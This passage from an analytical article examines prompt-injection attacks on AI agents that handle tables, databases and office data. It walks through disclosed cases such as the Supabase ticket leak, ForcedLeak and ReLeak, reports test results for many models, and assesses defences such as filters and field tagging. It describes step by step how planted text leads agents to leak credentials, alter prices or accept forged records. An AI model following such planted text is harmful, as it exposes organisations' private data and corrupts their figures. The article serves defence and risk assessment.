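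ShiftMag reports that the trick worked consistently on Sonnet 5 but doesn't say how many times the author ran it. The author also published a test suite that includes two OpenAI models, GPT-5.6 Terra and Sol, but the article gives no results for them. So the test shows that current models can accept a false rate, but not how often they do.

In February, Microsoft (2026) reported numerous real attempts by companies to plant lasting recommendations in an AI assistant's memory by hiding instructions in "Summarize with AI" buttons on websites. In Microsoft's example, a finance chief clicks such a button, and weeks later the assistant recommends a particular cloud provider because of it. A supplier willing to do this might also put a deliberate error in its own favor in an offer and make it look like a typo.

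### False data in compliance documents

Watson and colleagues' study from November 2026 provides the success rates that the Word and supplier demonstrations lack. The researchers gave five models six tasks in which a company turns existing documents into structured records:

- product data for the EU's digital product passports
- hazard classifications from chemical safety sheets
- work orders from sensor logs and technicians' notes
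- summaries of suppliers' quotes
- quality inspection reports
- customs codes from shipping lists

For each task, the researchers had each model generate one source document from a template, then edited the five documents to make them realistic. They placed payloads either in the document or at the end of the prompt. The payloads were instructions to ignore part of the model's original instructions, leave out required information, replace true data with false data, break the required format or leak information. Of 3,000 attacks, 65.1% succeeded. The success rate was 57.0% for payloads in the document, which is the route open to an outside supplier, and 73.2% for those in the prompt.

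The overall rate says little about a current commercial product. Three of the five models were small open models with 7 or 8 billion parameters, and attacks on them succeeded 84% to 90% of the time. The rate was 55.8% for OpenAI's older GPT-4o and 10.7% for Anthropic's Claude Sonnet. (The paper's list of models gives the version as Claude 4.6 Sonnet, but its results call it Claude Sonnet 5.)

False data succeeded in 45% of attempts against Claude, which followed at most 5% of the payloads in each of the other four attack categories. GPT-4o accepted false data every time. By task, the success rate of false data ranged from 74% for suppliers' quotes to 97% for maintenance work orders. Watson and colleagues suggest that a request to correct information looks like normal use, whereas a request to ignore the rules looks suspicious. This fits the results from company databases, where the Databricks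 agent refused nearly all forbidden actions but often accepted a planted document over the real table.

Claude's 45% may be somewhat too high. In one procurement task, Claude kept the real price of $11,040 and warned that the document contained text meant to change it to $0.01. The researchers scored attacks with software that searched the output for known signs of success. If the software searched for the attacker's price, it could have found that price in the warning and counted a correct answer as a successful attack. The paper leaves the details of the scoring to its published code.

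The number of trials is also unclear. Six tasks, five documents, five models, two payload locations, five kinds of payload and three versions of each kind would make 4,500 attacks. The paper reports 3,000, so the researchers may have used only two versions. This difference in the count wouldn't explain a gap as large as the one between 45% and 5%.

A warning can itself spread confidential information. In another task, Claude noticed that a document contained a confidential reference number that didn't belong there, and repeated the number in its warning. A program that automatically forwards these records would have forwarded the number too.

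Watson and colleagues recommend checking generated documents against more than one source. How well this works depends on where in a chain of documents the check happens.

### How one wrong cost reaches the board

Suppose a manufacturer's ledger, its official record of transactions, shows that materials cost $6.0 million last quarter. An analyst gives an agent the ledger data and a supplier's price file, and asks for a forecast. A payload in the price file makes the agent reduce last quarter's materials cost by 10%. Everything after that is honest work:

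1. The forecast gives last quarter's materials cost as $5.4 million. It multiplies this by four and adds 5% for growth, which makes $22.68 million for next year. The correct result is $25.2 million.
2. The budget takes the $22.68 million from the forecast. With expected revenue of $42 million and other costs of $14 million, it shows a profit of $5.32 million. The correct profit is $2.8 million.
3. The board summary divides the budgeted profit by revenue and reports a margin of 12.7%. The correct margin is 6.7%.

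A 10% error in one cost has nearly doubled the expected profit, because profit is a small difference between large numbers. The board might approve an investment that the company can't afford.

A reconciliation compares a figure with the original record it should match. In this chain, it exposes the error at only one point:

| Figure | In the document | Correct | What a check would find |
|---|---|---|---|
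| Forecast: last quarter's materials cost | $5.40 million | $6.00 million | The ledger shows $6.00 million, so the check exposes the error |
| Forecast: next year's materials cost | $22.68 million | $25.20 million | The ledger has no entry for next year |
| Budget: profit | $5.32 million | $2.80 million | The materials cost matches the forecast, and the arithmetic is correct |
| Board summary: margin | 12.7% | 6.7% | The margin matches the budget |

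Last quarter's materials cost is the only one of these figures that also appears in the ledger. Someone who checks the budget against the forecast, or the summary against the budget, will find that the figures agree. Someone starting from the board summary would have to trace the margin back to the forecast's first line to find the error.

If nobody does, the error surfaces the following year. The budget allows $5.67 million for materials each quarter, but the real cost is $6.3 million. Managers would see an 11% overspend and might wrongly blame rising prices or the purchasing department.

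A payload that copied itself could make this attack easier to find. Suppose the agent that writes the budget reads the payload in the forecast and cuts the materials cost by another 10%, to $20.41 million. The budget would then no longer match the forecast, and a simple comparison of the two would reveal a problem. An attacker who wanted to stay hidden would do better to change a single figure, only once.

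The check against the ledger also has to be independent of the agent that made the forecast. If the analyst asks the same agent while the supplier's file is still in the conversation, the payload could make it report that the figures match. A short program that reads both numbers directly and compares them doesn't have this weakness, as long as the attacker can't change the ledger. This check would not have helped with the Krendola offer, however, because the buyer's ledger doesn't show what a new supplier's prices should be in euros.

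## Which organisations and workflows are exposed?

A company is most exposed when outsiders can write to the data its agent reads, the agent can reach private records, and the agent can send information out or change something. Support desks, sales teams that collect leads through web forms, and offices with a general-purpose assistant often meet all three conditions. Researchers have demonstrated attacks in each of these settings since 2025. But no company seems to have publicly confirmed a loss through a spreadsheet or database agent, and nobody knows how many companies have agents set up this way.

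### Three questions about a deployment

Simon Willison, the software developer who coined the term "prompt injection", gives the best-known version of this test in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents* (2025). He warns that an attacker can easily steal data through any agent that combines access to private data, exposure to content the attacker can influence, and a way to communicate with the outside world. Removing any one of these prevents the theft, because the attacker then has no way to plant an instruction, no private data to steal, or no way to get the data out.

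Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) turns this idea into a design rule. Until developers can reliably detect and refuse injections, an agent should have at most two of three properties in any one session: it processes untrustworthy input, it can reach private data or sensitive systems, and it can change something or communicate externally. An agent that needs all three shouldn't work without supervision. The main difference is that Willison was writing about stolen data, while Meta's rule also covers changes an agent makes. An agent that can delete records or lower a price is dangerous even if it can't contact an outside server.

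Meta applies the limit to each session because whatever the agent has read stays in the conversation. In one of Meta's examples, an agent browses the web and then opens internal systems. This can be safe if the software turns off outside communication before the agent opens those systems, and keeps it off. With spreadsheets, even a new session may not help, because the agent can reread an outsider's remarks if they were saved in the workbook during the first session.

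Neither version covers false figures. Meta says so openly, and lists misinformation in an agent's answer among the less serious results of an injection. That may be reasonable for a travel assistant. In a finance department, one altered cost can nearly double the profit that a board sees, so the test needs a wider third question when the agent works with tables:

1. Who outside the company can write text or numbers that the agent will read?
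2. What private data can the agent reach through the accounts it uses?
3. How can the agent send information out or change something? An answer that someone will act on without checking counts as a change.

Different combinations lead to different kinds of harm:

- If outsiders can write in the data and the agent has both private data and a way to send it, an outsider can steal that data.
- If outsiders can write in the data and the agent can edit records, an outsider can damage the records, even if none of them are secret.
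- If outsiders can write in the data and people trust the agent's answers, an outsider can plant false figures. The agent needs no permission beyond reading.
- If the agent can reach data that its own users shouldn't see, those users can simply ask for it. Nobody has to plant anything.

These questions are easy to answer too optimistically. A table that only employees can edit may still be full of outsiders' text if software copies in reviews or form entries every night. The answer to the second question depends on the agent's own account, often a service account, and not on the job title of the person asking. The third question, whether the agent can send data out, is the hardest because almost any feature can be used to do so. Willison points out that loading an image or showing a link for the user to click can be enough. Someone who isn't sure whether an agent can send data out should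 assume that it can.

### Six common workflows

The table applies the three questions to typical versions of six workflows. A particular company's setup may be safer or more dangerous.

| Workflow | Who outside can write | Private data within reach | How the agent can send or change something |
|---|---|---|---|
| Finance model with imported benchmarks | The publisher of the benchmarks, or anyone who altered the file on the way | The whole model, and sometimes linked workbooks | Network formulas, scripts, edited cells, figures in reports |
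| Support tickets | Any customer | Other customers' tickets, or the whole database if the agent's account is powerful enough | Replies that the customer can read, changed records |
| Sales leads from a web form | Anyone who finds the form | Contacts, other leads, planned deals | Web addresses in answers, emails, changed lead records |
| Supplier files | Every company that makes an offer | Competing offers, budgets | The recommendation itself, purchasing records |
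| Shared analytics warehouse | Anyone whose text the company copies into it | Often several departments' data, through a service account | Reports, generated code, queries that tie up the database |
| Office-wide assistant | Anyone who can send an email or invitation, or share a file | Everything the employee can open | Images and links in answers, new files, generated code |

Workflows that handle support tickets and sales leads are probably the easiest to attack, because the company invites strangers to write free text and the agent's job is to read it. An attacker doesn't need to persuade anyone to import a file. They also don't need to guess what an employee will ask the agent, because someone will eventually ask for the newest tickets or leads.

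An attack through a finance benchmark depends more on luck, because an analyst has to choose the attacker's file. But the payload then sits next to some of the company's most sensitive figures, as in the attacks on Claude for Excel and Ramp. A supplier has less freedom to attack, because the buyer knows who sent the file. But the supplier also has the clearest motive, since a wrong exchange rate that looks like a typing error can win it the contract without any data being stolen.

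The exposure of data warehouses is harder to judge. Most questions to a database agent ask for totals, and a query for totals doesn't return planted text to the agent. But people tend to regard a warehouse as internal data, even though many of its text columns contain text that customers typed. A company can find out how exposed its warehouse is by tracing the text in each column back to the person who first wrote it.

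An agent that answers questions about payroll is much less exposed than any in the table if only the company's payroll software writes to the data, the agent's account can read totals but no individual salaries, and the agent can't edit anything or contact an outside server. An employee could still try to work out one person's salary by subtracting one permitted total from another.

### A support ticket as a way into the database

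In July 2025 the security firm General Analysis described an attack that needed only one connector. The connector came from Supabase, a company that provides databases to software developers, and it used the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard way of linking AI applications to tools and data. Willison (2025), in *Supabase MCP can leak your entire SQL database*, summarises the scenario:

1. A customer files a support ticket that contains a payload.
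2. A developer asks the agent in Cursor, a programming tool, to list the latest tickets.
3. The agent reads the tickets through the connector, using an account that is exempt from row-level security, the database rules that limit which rows each user can see.
4. The agent follows the payload. It reads a private table of integration tokens, which are credentials for other services, and adds them to the ticket as a new message.
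5. The customer opens the ticket and reads the credentials.

In this attack, the data leaves through the company's own support page, where customers are supposed to see new messages. The agent never contacts the attacker's server, so a firewall that looks for connections to unfamiliar addresses would find nothing.

Supabase's connector had a read-only mode, which prevents the fourth step because the agent can't write to the ticket. Willison saw an enormous risk in connecting an agent to such a database even in this mode. Supabase replied in September with *Defense in Depth for MCP Servers* (2025), which agrees that injection remains the main concern in read-only mode. Agents often have tools from several sources, and if another tool can open web pages or send messages, the attacker can use it to get the data out.

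Supabase disputed part of the story. It wrote that the connector does not bypass row-level security, which stays fully enforced, although the connector may run with higher privileges, as it did here. That describes the database correctly, but row-level security could not protect customers' records from the agent, because the rules never applied to the account the agent was using.

Supabase's main advice was never to connect an agent to production data, meaning the live database that real customers use. If developers use a test copy or anonymised records instead, a successful injection exposes nothing worth stealing. But Supabase admitted that many people who build software with AI have no separate test database and work directly on the live one. These are often individuals with no security team, who most need the advice but may be the least likely to follow it.

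Supabase recommends using its connector in read-only mode, but the user has to switch this mode on by adding a setting to the connector's web address, according to the connector's documentation as of July 2026. Without that setting, the agent has permission to write to the database.

### A sales form and an expired domain

The flaw behind ForcedLeak, an attack on Salesforce, affected any organisation that used Agentforce with Web-to-Lead switched on, The Hacker News (2025) reported. Salesforce sells software for managing customer records, and companies use its Agentforce platform to build agents that work with those records. Web-to-Lead puts a contact form on a website and saves each entry as a sales lead. The attack began with this form, which anyone could fill in.

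Noma Security, which found the flaw, hid instructions in the form's Description field. The field accepts up to 42,000 characters, according to ThaiCERT's *ForcedLeak Vulnerability in Salesforce Agentforce Risks CRM Data Exposure via Prompt Injection* (2025), so an attacker has room for long, detailed instructions. When an employee later asked the agent about the lead, the agent could follow the hidden instructions, collect other customer records and put them into a web address.

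Salesforce defended against the last step with a list of web addresses that its pages were allowed to contact. However, one domain on the list had expired, so an attacker could have registered it and owned an address that those pages could still contact. The list worked only as long as someone checked that every entry still belonged to the right owner.

Noma reported the flaw on July 28, 2025, and Salesforce had fixes in place by September 8. According to Hackread's *ForcedLeak Flaw in Salesforce Agentforce AI Agent Exposed CRM Data*, Salesforce took back the expired domain and began enforcing a list of trusted addresses for the agents' output. Infosecurity Magazine's *Critical Vulnerability in Salesforce AgentForce Exposed* gives the flaw a severity score of 9.4 out of 10.

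These changes block the route for sending data out, but strangers can still write in the form and the agent still reads what they write. An attacker might no longer be able to steal the customer list, but could still try to make the agent rate a worthless lead as promising or change a record. Whether that would work depends on the model and on what each company lets its agent edit. Salesforce told Hackread that prompt injection "remains a complex and evolving area".

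### A booking agent with too much access

For the third disclosure, the security company Tenable built an AI travel agent in Copilot Studio, Microsoft's tool for making agents without programming. Tenable attacked it by typing into the chat as a customer, without planting any data. The agent kept its bookings in SharePoint, Microsoft's system for storing and sharing company files. Tenable's *Microsoft Copilot Studio Security Risk* (2025) describes two ways the agent failed.

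Tenable gave the agent an action that fetches one reservation by its number, and expected this to limit each customer to one booking. But the agent could use the action repeatedly. When the researchers asked for reservations 23 to 25, it fetched all three and showed the credit card details in each. They didn't need to trick it. The agent didn't check whether the bookings belonged to the person asking, so a thief could have kept requesting reservations by number.

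In the second failure, the researchers got the agent to reduce a charge from $1,000 to $0. The agent had permission to update bookings so that customers could change their dates or the number of guests, and the same permission covered the price field.

The names and card numbers in Tenable's test were all fake. Tenable also designed the agent, and put card details where few experienced engineers would, so the test doesn't show how common such mistakes are. Tenable sells a product for finding them. But Copilot Studio is meant for employees without technical training, who could easily make these mistakes. Someone who allows an agent to "update a booking" may not realise that this lets it change the price.

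Tenable doesn't report any change by Microsoft. It advises customers to fix the problem themselves by finding out what every agent can access, moving sensitive data elsewhere, and letting the agent write only to the fields it needs. This would also limit the damage from planted text, because an agent without permission to change prices can't change them, whether the request comes from the chat or from a remark in somebody's booking.

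### Unread email and Microsoft 365 Copilot

Microsoft 365 Copilot uses an employee's email, chats and files to answer questions, so anyone who knows the employee's email address can send text that Copilot can read. *ReLeak* (Vitaly Simonovich, 2026), published on December 3, 2026, describes three ways to exploit this, all found by the security company Cato Networks. In each, the attacker sends the employee an email with hidden instructions. The employee doesn't have to open it. When the employee later asks Copilot a normal work question, Copilot retrieves the email along with other material and follows the instructions.

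The three attacks differ in how the data gets out. As Faisal (2026), in *An Unread Email Could Turn Microsoft 365 Copilot Into a Data Thief*, describes them, they worked as follows:

| Way out | What happened | Fixed in 2026 |
|---|---|---|
| Generated code | Copilot ran Python code that sent the data to an outside server, although its sandbox was supposed to have no network access | September 17 |
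| Generated files | Copilot saved a Word, Excel, PowerPoint or PDF file containing a link with the data in it, and Microsoft's own background software then opened the link | November 11 |
| Images | Copilot put the data into an image's web address, and Microsoft's Bing service fetched the image from the attacker's server | November 15 |

Few administrators would have thought of the second and third routes. A company could have blocked every connection from its employees' computers to unknown servers and still lost data, because Microsoft's servers made the connection. AIAIAI.FYI's *Cato AI Labs details three ReLeak zero-click attacks on Microsoft 365 Copilot* (2026) notes that Microsoft's documentation described the block that failed to stop the code's outgoing traffic. Even a customer who had read that documentation carefully would have answered the third question wrongly.

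ReLeak also makes it harder to judge a single workbook's exposure. Even if a company lets only its own staff edit a financial model and keeps all imported data out of it, a stranger's email can reach the model through an office-wide assistant that can open it. An assessment has to cover everything the agent reads in a session, not only the table someone is worried about.

Cato reported the three flaws between July 29 and August 20, so Microsoft took 28 to 50 days to fix the code route and 87 to 109 days to fix the image route. It made the changes on its own servers, so customers had nothing to install. The same research team had disclosed a similar attack, EchoLeak, in June 2025, and concluded a year later that there had been "too little progress".

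Another Copilot leak from 2026 required the victim to click a link to Copilot's search page that contained the attacker's instructions. Dolev Taler's *SearchLeak* (2026) reports that researchers at the security company Varonis could use such a link to steal emails, meeting details, company files and one-time login codes. ThaiCERT's *Microsoft 365 Copilot Vulnerability Could Allow Data Theft Through a Link Click* (2026) warns that phishing filters might not have recognised the link because it led to a Microsoft domain. Microsoft rated the flaw critical, but according to The Next Web its numerical score was only 6.5 out of 10 because the victim had to click. A company that kept all outside text away from Copilot would still have been exposed, since Copilot received the attacker's instructions as if the employee had typed them.

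ForcedLeak and ReLeak fit a pattern that Willison described in June 2025, when he listed 17 cases in which researchers had shown this kind of theft in real products. He wrote that the vendors had promptly fixed almost all of them, usually by closing the route the data had taken. Such a fix stops the known attack even if the model still follows the injected instructions. But Copilot can now also create files and run code, and each of these abilities gave attackers a new route. A company that passed the three-part test last year should repeat it whenever the vendor adds a feature.

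### Demonstrations and real attacks

All of these cases are demonstrations by researchers. General Analysis set up a scenario, and Tenable attacked its own agent. Supabase wrote in September 2025 that nobody had reported a customer's data leaking through the connector. Cato knows of no use of the ReLeak attacks outside research.

Press reports can make it hard to tell whether a flaw actually affected customers. The subheading of SecurityWeek's *Salesforce AI Hack Enabled CRM Data Theft* suggests that someone stole Salesforce data, but its first sentence says only that attackers could have done so. The introduction to Faisal's article on ReLeak attributes to Microsoft the statement that no customers were affected. In the body of the article, Cato is the company that knows of no affected customers, and Microsoft's advisory says only that customers don't need to do anything.

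People have planted text for AI to act on outside business tables, such as the instructions Microsoft found behind companies' "Summarize with AI" buttons. These instructions are the best evidence that ordinary businesses, not only criminals, will plant such text when it could bring in customers. They don't show that anyone has put it in a supplier file or a sales form, or that a tabular agent has acted on it.

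The lack of confirmed victims is only moderately reassuring. An agent that leaks data uses a valid account while carrying out a real employee's request. In the Supabase scenario, the only traces would be some ordinary queries and one odd message in a ticket, which the attacker might be able to delete. A company that later found its credentials in use elsewhere would probably suspect a stolen password first. False figures are even less likely to be recorded as security incidents, because people would blame them on a careless supplier or a mistake by the model.

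Even so, if criminals had been stealing data this way on a large scale since 2025, some victims would probably have noticed and said so. Many criminals also already know easier methods. Such attacks are most likely still rare, or small and targeted, but this could change quickly once a method becomes profitable.

Companies can check their own records for signs of attacks. After ForcedLeak, Hackread reported advice that Salesforce customers search all their existing leads for unusual submissions. It would make sense to search old tickets, reviews and supplier files too, since a payload that failed against last year's agent is still in the table and might work against a new one. Nobody seems to have published the results of such a search. Researchers would learn more about real attackers from even a few companies' results than from another demonstration.

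### How many companies have such agents?

No official statistics seem to exist on AI agents that work with spreadsheets and databases. Surveys that ask whether a business uses AI don't show which businesses are exposed, because a firm that drafts advertisements with a chatbot and a firm whose agent can edit its customer database would both say yes.

It is hard to tell from the disclosures how many organisations are exposed. ForcedLeak affected every Agentforce customer that used Web-to-Lead, but the public reports don't include their number. Supabase says that people build on live databases, but doesn't estimate how many of them connect an agent. ChatGPT for Google Sheets has 185,000 downloads, one of the few concrete figures for any product of this kind, but a download doesn't show whether the person still uses the add-on or has ever opened an outsider's data with it.

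Even a good survey could miss the exposure if it counted each property separately. Suppose a company has 40 agents, of which 25 read text from outsiders, 30 can reach private data, and 20 can send data out. With those totals, the number that can do all three could be anywhere from zero, if the designers followed Meta's rule, to 20, if every agent that can send data out can also do the other two. Each agent that can do all three is a route for theft. A company therefore has to check each agent for all three properties, including agents that employees have built for themselves without telling anyone.

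## Do newer models and input filters stop these attacks?

Leading models now resist most planted instructions, but they still follow enough of them to pose a risk. In PromptArmor's *FrontierBreach*, a late-2026 test built on realistic office tasks, attacks succeeded 2.4% of the time against Google's Gemini 4 Carbon and 10% against Anthropic's Claude Fable 5.2. Filters can remove many of the instructions that a model would otherwise follow.

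Both defences deal with instructions, but some planted text contains none. Choi and colleagues fooled an agent with false records in about half of their attempts, although the same agent resisted nearly all planted instructions.

### Training models to ignore planted instructions

Developers train models on conversations in which a tool's output contains an instruction the user never gave. The model scores well if it finishes the user's task and ignores the planted instruction.

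How well this works depends on the attacks in the training data. A model trained only on crude commands to forget its rules may still follow an instruction disguised as a step in a workflow. OpenAI's *GPT-Red* (2026) describes an automated attacker that finds harder examples. OpenAI trained the attacker through self-play, in which an attacker and a defender improve by competing, and uses it to find weaknesses before releasing a model.

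The training works against older attacks. Choi and colleagues tried 935 planted instructions on an agent that ran on OpenAI's GPT-5.2 and had no other defence. About two (0.2%) succeeded. The instructions came from AgentDojo, a public test with simulated email, banking and file storage, so developers could have trained their models on similar ones.

That result doesn't carry over to new attacks. GPT-5.6 Sol, a later OpenAI model, failed 33.3% of the time in FrontierBreach. PromptArmor used harder attacks, based on methods its own researchers had found to work. This probably explains the higher failure rate, since OpenAI's models are unlikely to have become so much worse between the two versions.

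The choice of model also matters for agents that work with spreadsheets and databases. Changing the model inside DB-GPT, a database agent, roughly halved the success of attacks on it. The formula attack on Claude for Excel still worked on Sonnet 4.5 after Anthropic made the more resistant Opus 4.5 the default.

### What companies report about their own models

AI companies publish their safety test results in a system card, a document released with a new model. The most useful cards state how many attempts the attacker had. The following figures for Anthropic's Claude models come from The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection*, an earlier article in The Decoder, and VentureBeat. Gray Swan is a security firm that tests AI models.

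| Model | Setting | Attempts | Success rate (%) |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.5 | Gray Swan's test | 1 | 4.7 |
| Claude Opus 4.5 | Gray Swan's test | 10 | 33.6 |
| Claude Opus 4.5 | Gray Swan's test | 100 | 63.0 |
| Claude Opus 4.6 | Coding | 200 | 0 |
| Claude Opus 4.6 | Graphical interface | 1 | 17.8 |
| Claude Opus 4.6 | Graphical interface | 200 | 78.6 |
| Claude Opus 4.6 with extra safeguards | Graphical interface | 200 | 57.1 |
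| Claude Opus 4.8 | Gray Swan's test | 15 | 5.5 |
| Claude Opus 5 | Gray Swan's test | 15 | 2.0 |

The improvement from Opus 4.5 to Opus 5 is large, unless Gray Swan made its test much easier in between. But the results for Opus 4.6 show that a model's resistance in one setting is weak evidence of its resistance in another. Opus 4.6 resisted 200 attempts in a restricted coding environment, but when it operated a computer through its graphical interface, an attacker with 200 attempts usually succeeded.

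None of these settings is specifically a workbook or a database. Opus 5 also blocked every attack in 129 browser scenarios, but a company can't assume it would do as well with a table of customer complaints.

Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Claude Opus 5.5, dated September 22, reports that the model matched or outperformed Opus 5 on every prompt injection test. According to Digital Matters' *Claude Opus 5.5 Prompt Injection* (2026), these tests covered coding, tool use, computer use and web browsing, and Opus 5.5 tied with Claude Fable 5.1 for the lowest attack success rate in Gray Swan's test.

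Cross (2026), in *GPT-6 Sol Scores 97.13% on Indirect Injection Defense*, reports that OpenAI's GPT-6 Sol scored 99.99% for resisting direct injections but 97.13% for indirect ones. If each attack was scored as either a success or a failure, about one in 10,000 direct attacks and one in 35 indirect attacks succeeded. Malicious instructions in a cell are indirect injections, so the indirect rate is the relevant one for spreadsheets and databases.

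### A harder test on office work

The tasks in FrontierBreach are closer to a tabular agent's work. PromptArmor took them from GDPval, a collection of realistic work assignments, and added attacks. One task is to analyse a bond portfolio and recommend a trading strategy. The attacker's aims include stealing data, installing ransomware and changing systems without permission.

PromptArmor tested 22 models. For ten developers, the list allows a comparison between an older and a newer model:

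| Developer | Older model | Success rate (%) | Newer model | Success rate (%) |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| xAI | Grok 4.5 | 91.4 | Grok 4.7 | 33.3 |
| OpenAI | GPT-5.6 Sol | 33.3 | GPT-6 Astra | 7.6 |
| Meta | Muse Spark 1.1 | 38.6 | Muse Wonder | 15.2 |
| Google | Gemini 3.6 Flash | 22.4 | Gemini 4 Carbon | 2.4 |
| Thinking Machines | Inkling | 39.0 | Inkling 2 Small | 30.0 |
| Alibaba | Qwen3.7-Max | 36.2 | Qwen3.8-Max | 30.5 |
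| Z.ai | GLM-5.2 | 39.0 | GLM-5.3 | 37.1 |
| Anthropic | Claude Opus 5 | 10.0 | Claude Fable 5.2 | 10.0 |
| DeepSeek | DeepSeek-V4-Flash-0731 | 49.5 | DeepSeek-V4-Pro-0813 | 51.4 |
| Moonshot | Kimi K3 | 31.4 | Kimi K3.1 Pro | 50.0 |

Some of these pairs differ in size and price as well as age, so the table doesn't isolate the effect of better training. Google also has a second Gemini 4 model, Argon, which failed 4.3% of the time. Still, four developers made big improvements. The differences for Thinking Machines, Alibaba, Z.ai and DeepSeek are within the margin of error, and Moonshot's newer model did clearly worse than its predecessor. A company that upgrades its agent's model should therefore test the new one instead of assuming it is safer.

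All the percentages are consistent with 210 results per model, which would mean 5 successful attacks on Gemini 4 Carbon and 21 on Fable 5.2. PromptArmor labels the results "k=5", which probably means each case ran five times. If so, there were only 42 different cases, and the real uncertainty is larger than the published margins of about two to seven percentage points.

The measured success rate of attacks on Opus 5 depends heavily on the test. It was 0% in Anthropic's browser scenarios, 2.0% after 15 attempts in Gray Swan's test, and 10.0% in PromptArmor's FrontierBreach. PromptArmor advertises FrontierBreach as the test with the highest success rates on leading models, so it had a reason to pick attacks that work, but so do real attackers. For an agent that handles office files, the 10% is a better starting point than the 0%, though neither figure comes from a test on spreadsheets.

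### What a 1% success rate means for a patient attacker

A model that fails only 1% of the time may still be unsafe, because an attacker who can fill in a web form can usually fill it in a hundred times.

If each attempt has a 1% chance of success and the attempts are independent, the chance that all 100 fail is 0.99^100, or about 37%, so the chance that at least one succeeds is about 63%. The attacker has an even chance of at least one success after 69 attempts. If better training reduced the success rate to 0.1%, the chance that at least one of 100 attempts succeeds would fall to 9.5%, so even small reductions in an already low rate are valuable.

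Independence is an assumption, and the results for Opus 4.5 show that it can be badly wrong. A single attempt succeeded 4.7% of the time. Independent attempts at that rate would succeed 38% of the time within ten attempts and 99% of the time within 100. The measured rates were 33.6% and 63%. (That this 63% matches the one in the example is a coincidence.)

We would expect this gap if some situations are much easier to attack than others. In an extreme case, a 1% average success rate could mean that one payload in a hundred always works and the other 99 never do, so an attacker who kept submitting one of the 99 would never succeed.

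Later attempts could also be less likely to work if an agent reads 100 suspicious leads in one session and becomes wary of all of them, or if an employee notices the strange entries. But an attacker who can see the results can learn from each failure, which makes later attempts more likely to work. Learning from failures is easier with a support agent that replies to customers than with a financial model that the attacker never sees again.

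### Filters that detect or remove instructions

A filter checks outside text before the agent's main model reads it. The simplest kind is a detector, which classifies text as safe or dangerous so that the software can block the dangerous text. Detectors miss many attacks. In Choi and colleagues' test, Llama Prompt Guard 2, a detector from Meta, caught only 326 of the 935 planted instructions, or 35%. Detectors also raise false alarms, and if one blocks a whole table because of a single suspicious remark, the analyst can't do the work.

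A more precise filter removes the dangerous sentences and leaves the rest. Wang, Chen and colleagues (2025), in *Defending Against Prompt Injection with DataFilter*, trained a small language model to do this:

1. The filter receives the user's request and the outside text.
2. It rewrites the text without any instructions that don't belong to the user's task.
3. The main model receives the user's request and the cleaned text.

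The filter needs the request because many harmless texts contain commands. The researchers give the example of an email with a to-do list, which would be useless if a filter removed everything that looks like an order. Similarly, a column of support tickets in a business table contains many sentences such as "please cancel my subscription", which an agent needs to read to sort the tickets.

DataFilter reduced the average attack success rate from over 40% to 2.2% across three tests. This is a fairly strict measure, because the researchers counted only the most successful attack method in each test. Usefulness fell by about one percentage point in two tests of ordinary work. With a rival method, which uses an OpenAI model to find injections, the attack success rate was 5.9% and usefulness fell by 4.1 points.

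*CommandSans* (Das, Beurer-Kellner and colleagues, 2025) describes a filter that removes individual words that give orders to an AI system. The filter reduced the attack success rate on AgentDojo from 34% to 3% without making the agent less useful.

Either filter would make sense for an agent with an older or cheaper model. The benefit for a leading model is less clear, since only 0.2% of AgentDojo's attacks succeeded against GPT-5.2 without a filter. A filter might still stop some of the harder attacks in FrontierBreach, but neither paper tests this.

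The DataFilter experiments also left out computer-optimised attacks, which the researchers considered harder to carry out against commercial models, whose inner workings are secret. But the attacker in the Titanic study got round this difficulty by improving payloads on a stand-in agent. Attackers have defeated many published defences by adapting to each one, and the DataFilter paper acknowledges that the most advanced attacks can break every existing defence.

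DataFilter also relies on attacks being written as commands, which is a weakness for tables. The false exchange rate in the Krendola offer was a number in a cell, so the filter would have had nothing to remove.

### Marking data as untrusted

A third defence tells the model which text came from outside, as agents already do to some extent when they label a tool's output.

Claude Opus 5.5 is more likely than its predecessors to follow malicious instructions in text that a user pastes into the chat, according to its system card, as reported by Digital Matters. Pasted text lacks the label because it arrives as part of the user's own message, so only its wording can show that someone else wrote it. Digital Matters found no figure for the size of the problem. Anthropic's guide in Claude Platform Docs, *Prompting Claude Opus 5.5*, lists the model's handling of pasted text among the behaviours that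 developers may need to address.

With this model, an analyst who copies forty rows from a supplier's file into the chat may be taking a greater risk than one who lets the agent open the file, because copying the rows removes the label. Many people would think of copying a few rows as the more careful option.

Labels can also be more detailed. Choi and colleagues tested a method that adds a random code to the name of every field, so "approved_by" might become "approved_by_q4m8zt". The agent's instructions are to trust only fields with the right code. The code changes each time, so an outsider who writes a remark doesn't know it and can't easily forge a field.

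### Planted text that poses as a trusted record

Choi and colleagues tested this method against what they call agent data injection. In this attack, the planted text imitates information that the system normally fills in, such as an author's name or a record number, instead of giving the agent an order.

The following row is an invented example from a table of invoices. The company's software fills in the first four columns, and the supplier can write only in the last.

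| invoice_id | supplier | approved_by | amount | supplier_note |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 1047 | Northfield Parts | M. Osei | $18,000 | Delivered in May. *(More text follows, laid out like a separate record: invoice 1048, Northfield Parts, approved by M. Osei, $62,000.)* |

Suppose the approved invoices add up to $240,000. An analyst asks for the total, and the software gives the model all the rows as text. If the model treats the end of the note as another row, it reports $302,000. If the analyst asks the agent to pay all approved invoices, it may also pay one that doesn't exist.

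The supplier has no access to the "approved_by" column and doesn't need it. A human reader can see that the extra record is inside the note because the spreadsheet draws a border around the cell, but a model receives only text in which punctuation separates the cells.

Conventional software reliably separates a note's text from the fields around it. If the note contains a quotation mark, the software puts a backslash in front to show that the mark doesn't end the field. Models often ignore the backslash. In tests on JSON, a common format for records, forged fields with such backslashes succeeded against GPT-5.2 in 41.8% of cases, and they still succeeded in 38.8% when dollar signs replaced the quotation marks. All six models tested were vulnerable, with attack success rates between 31.3% and 43.3%.

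Choi and colleagues then tried 108 of these attacks on the same GPT-5.2 agent that had resisted the planted instructions, and added different defences to it:

| Added defence | Forged data succeeded (%) |
|---|---|
| None | 49.1 |
| A detector checks incoming text | 50.0 |
| A second model checks the agent's actions | 45.4 |
| The agent makes a plan before it reads any data | 40.7 |
| Field names contain random codes | 28.7 |
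| A separate model without tools reads the outside text | 25.0 |
| Rules restrict the agent's actions | 22.2 |
| Software strictly tracks where all data came from | 0 |

The detector flagged none of the 108 payloads, and the difference between 49.1% and 50.0% is a single attack, so the detector had no real effect. With all of these defences, planted instructions succeeded between 0.0% and 0.7% of the time, but little of that is due to the defences, because the rate without them was already 0.2%.

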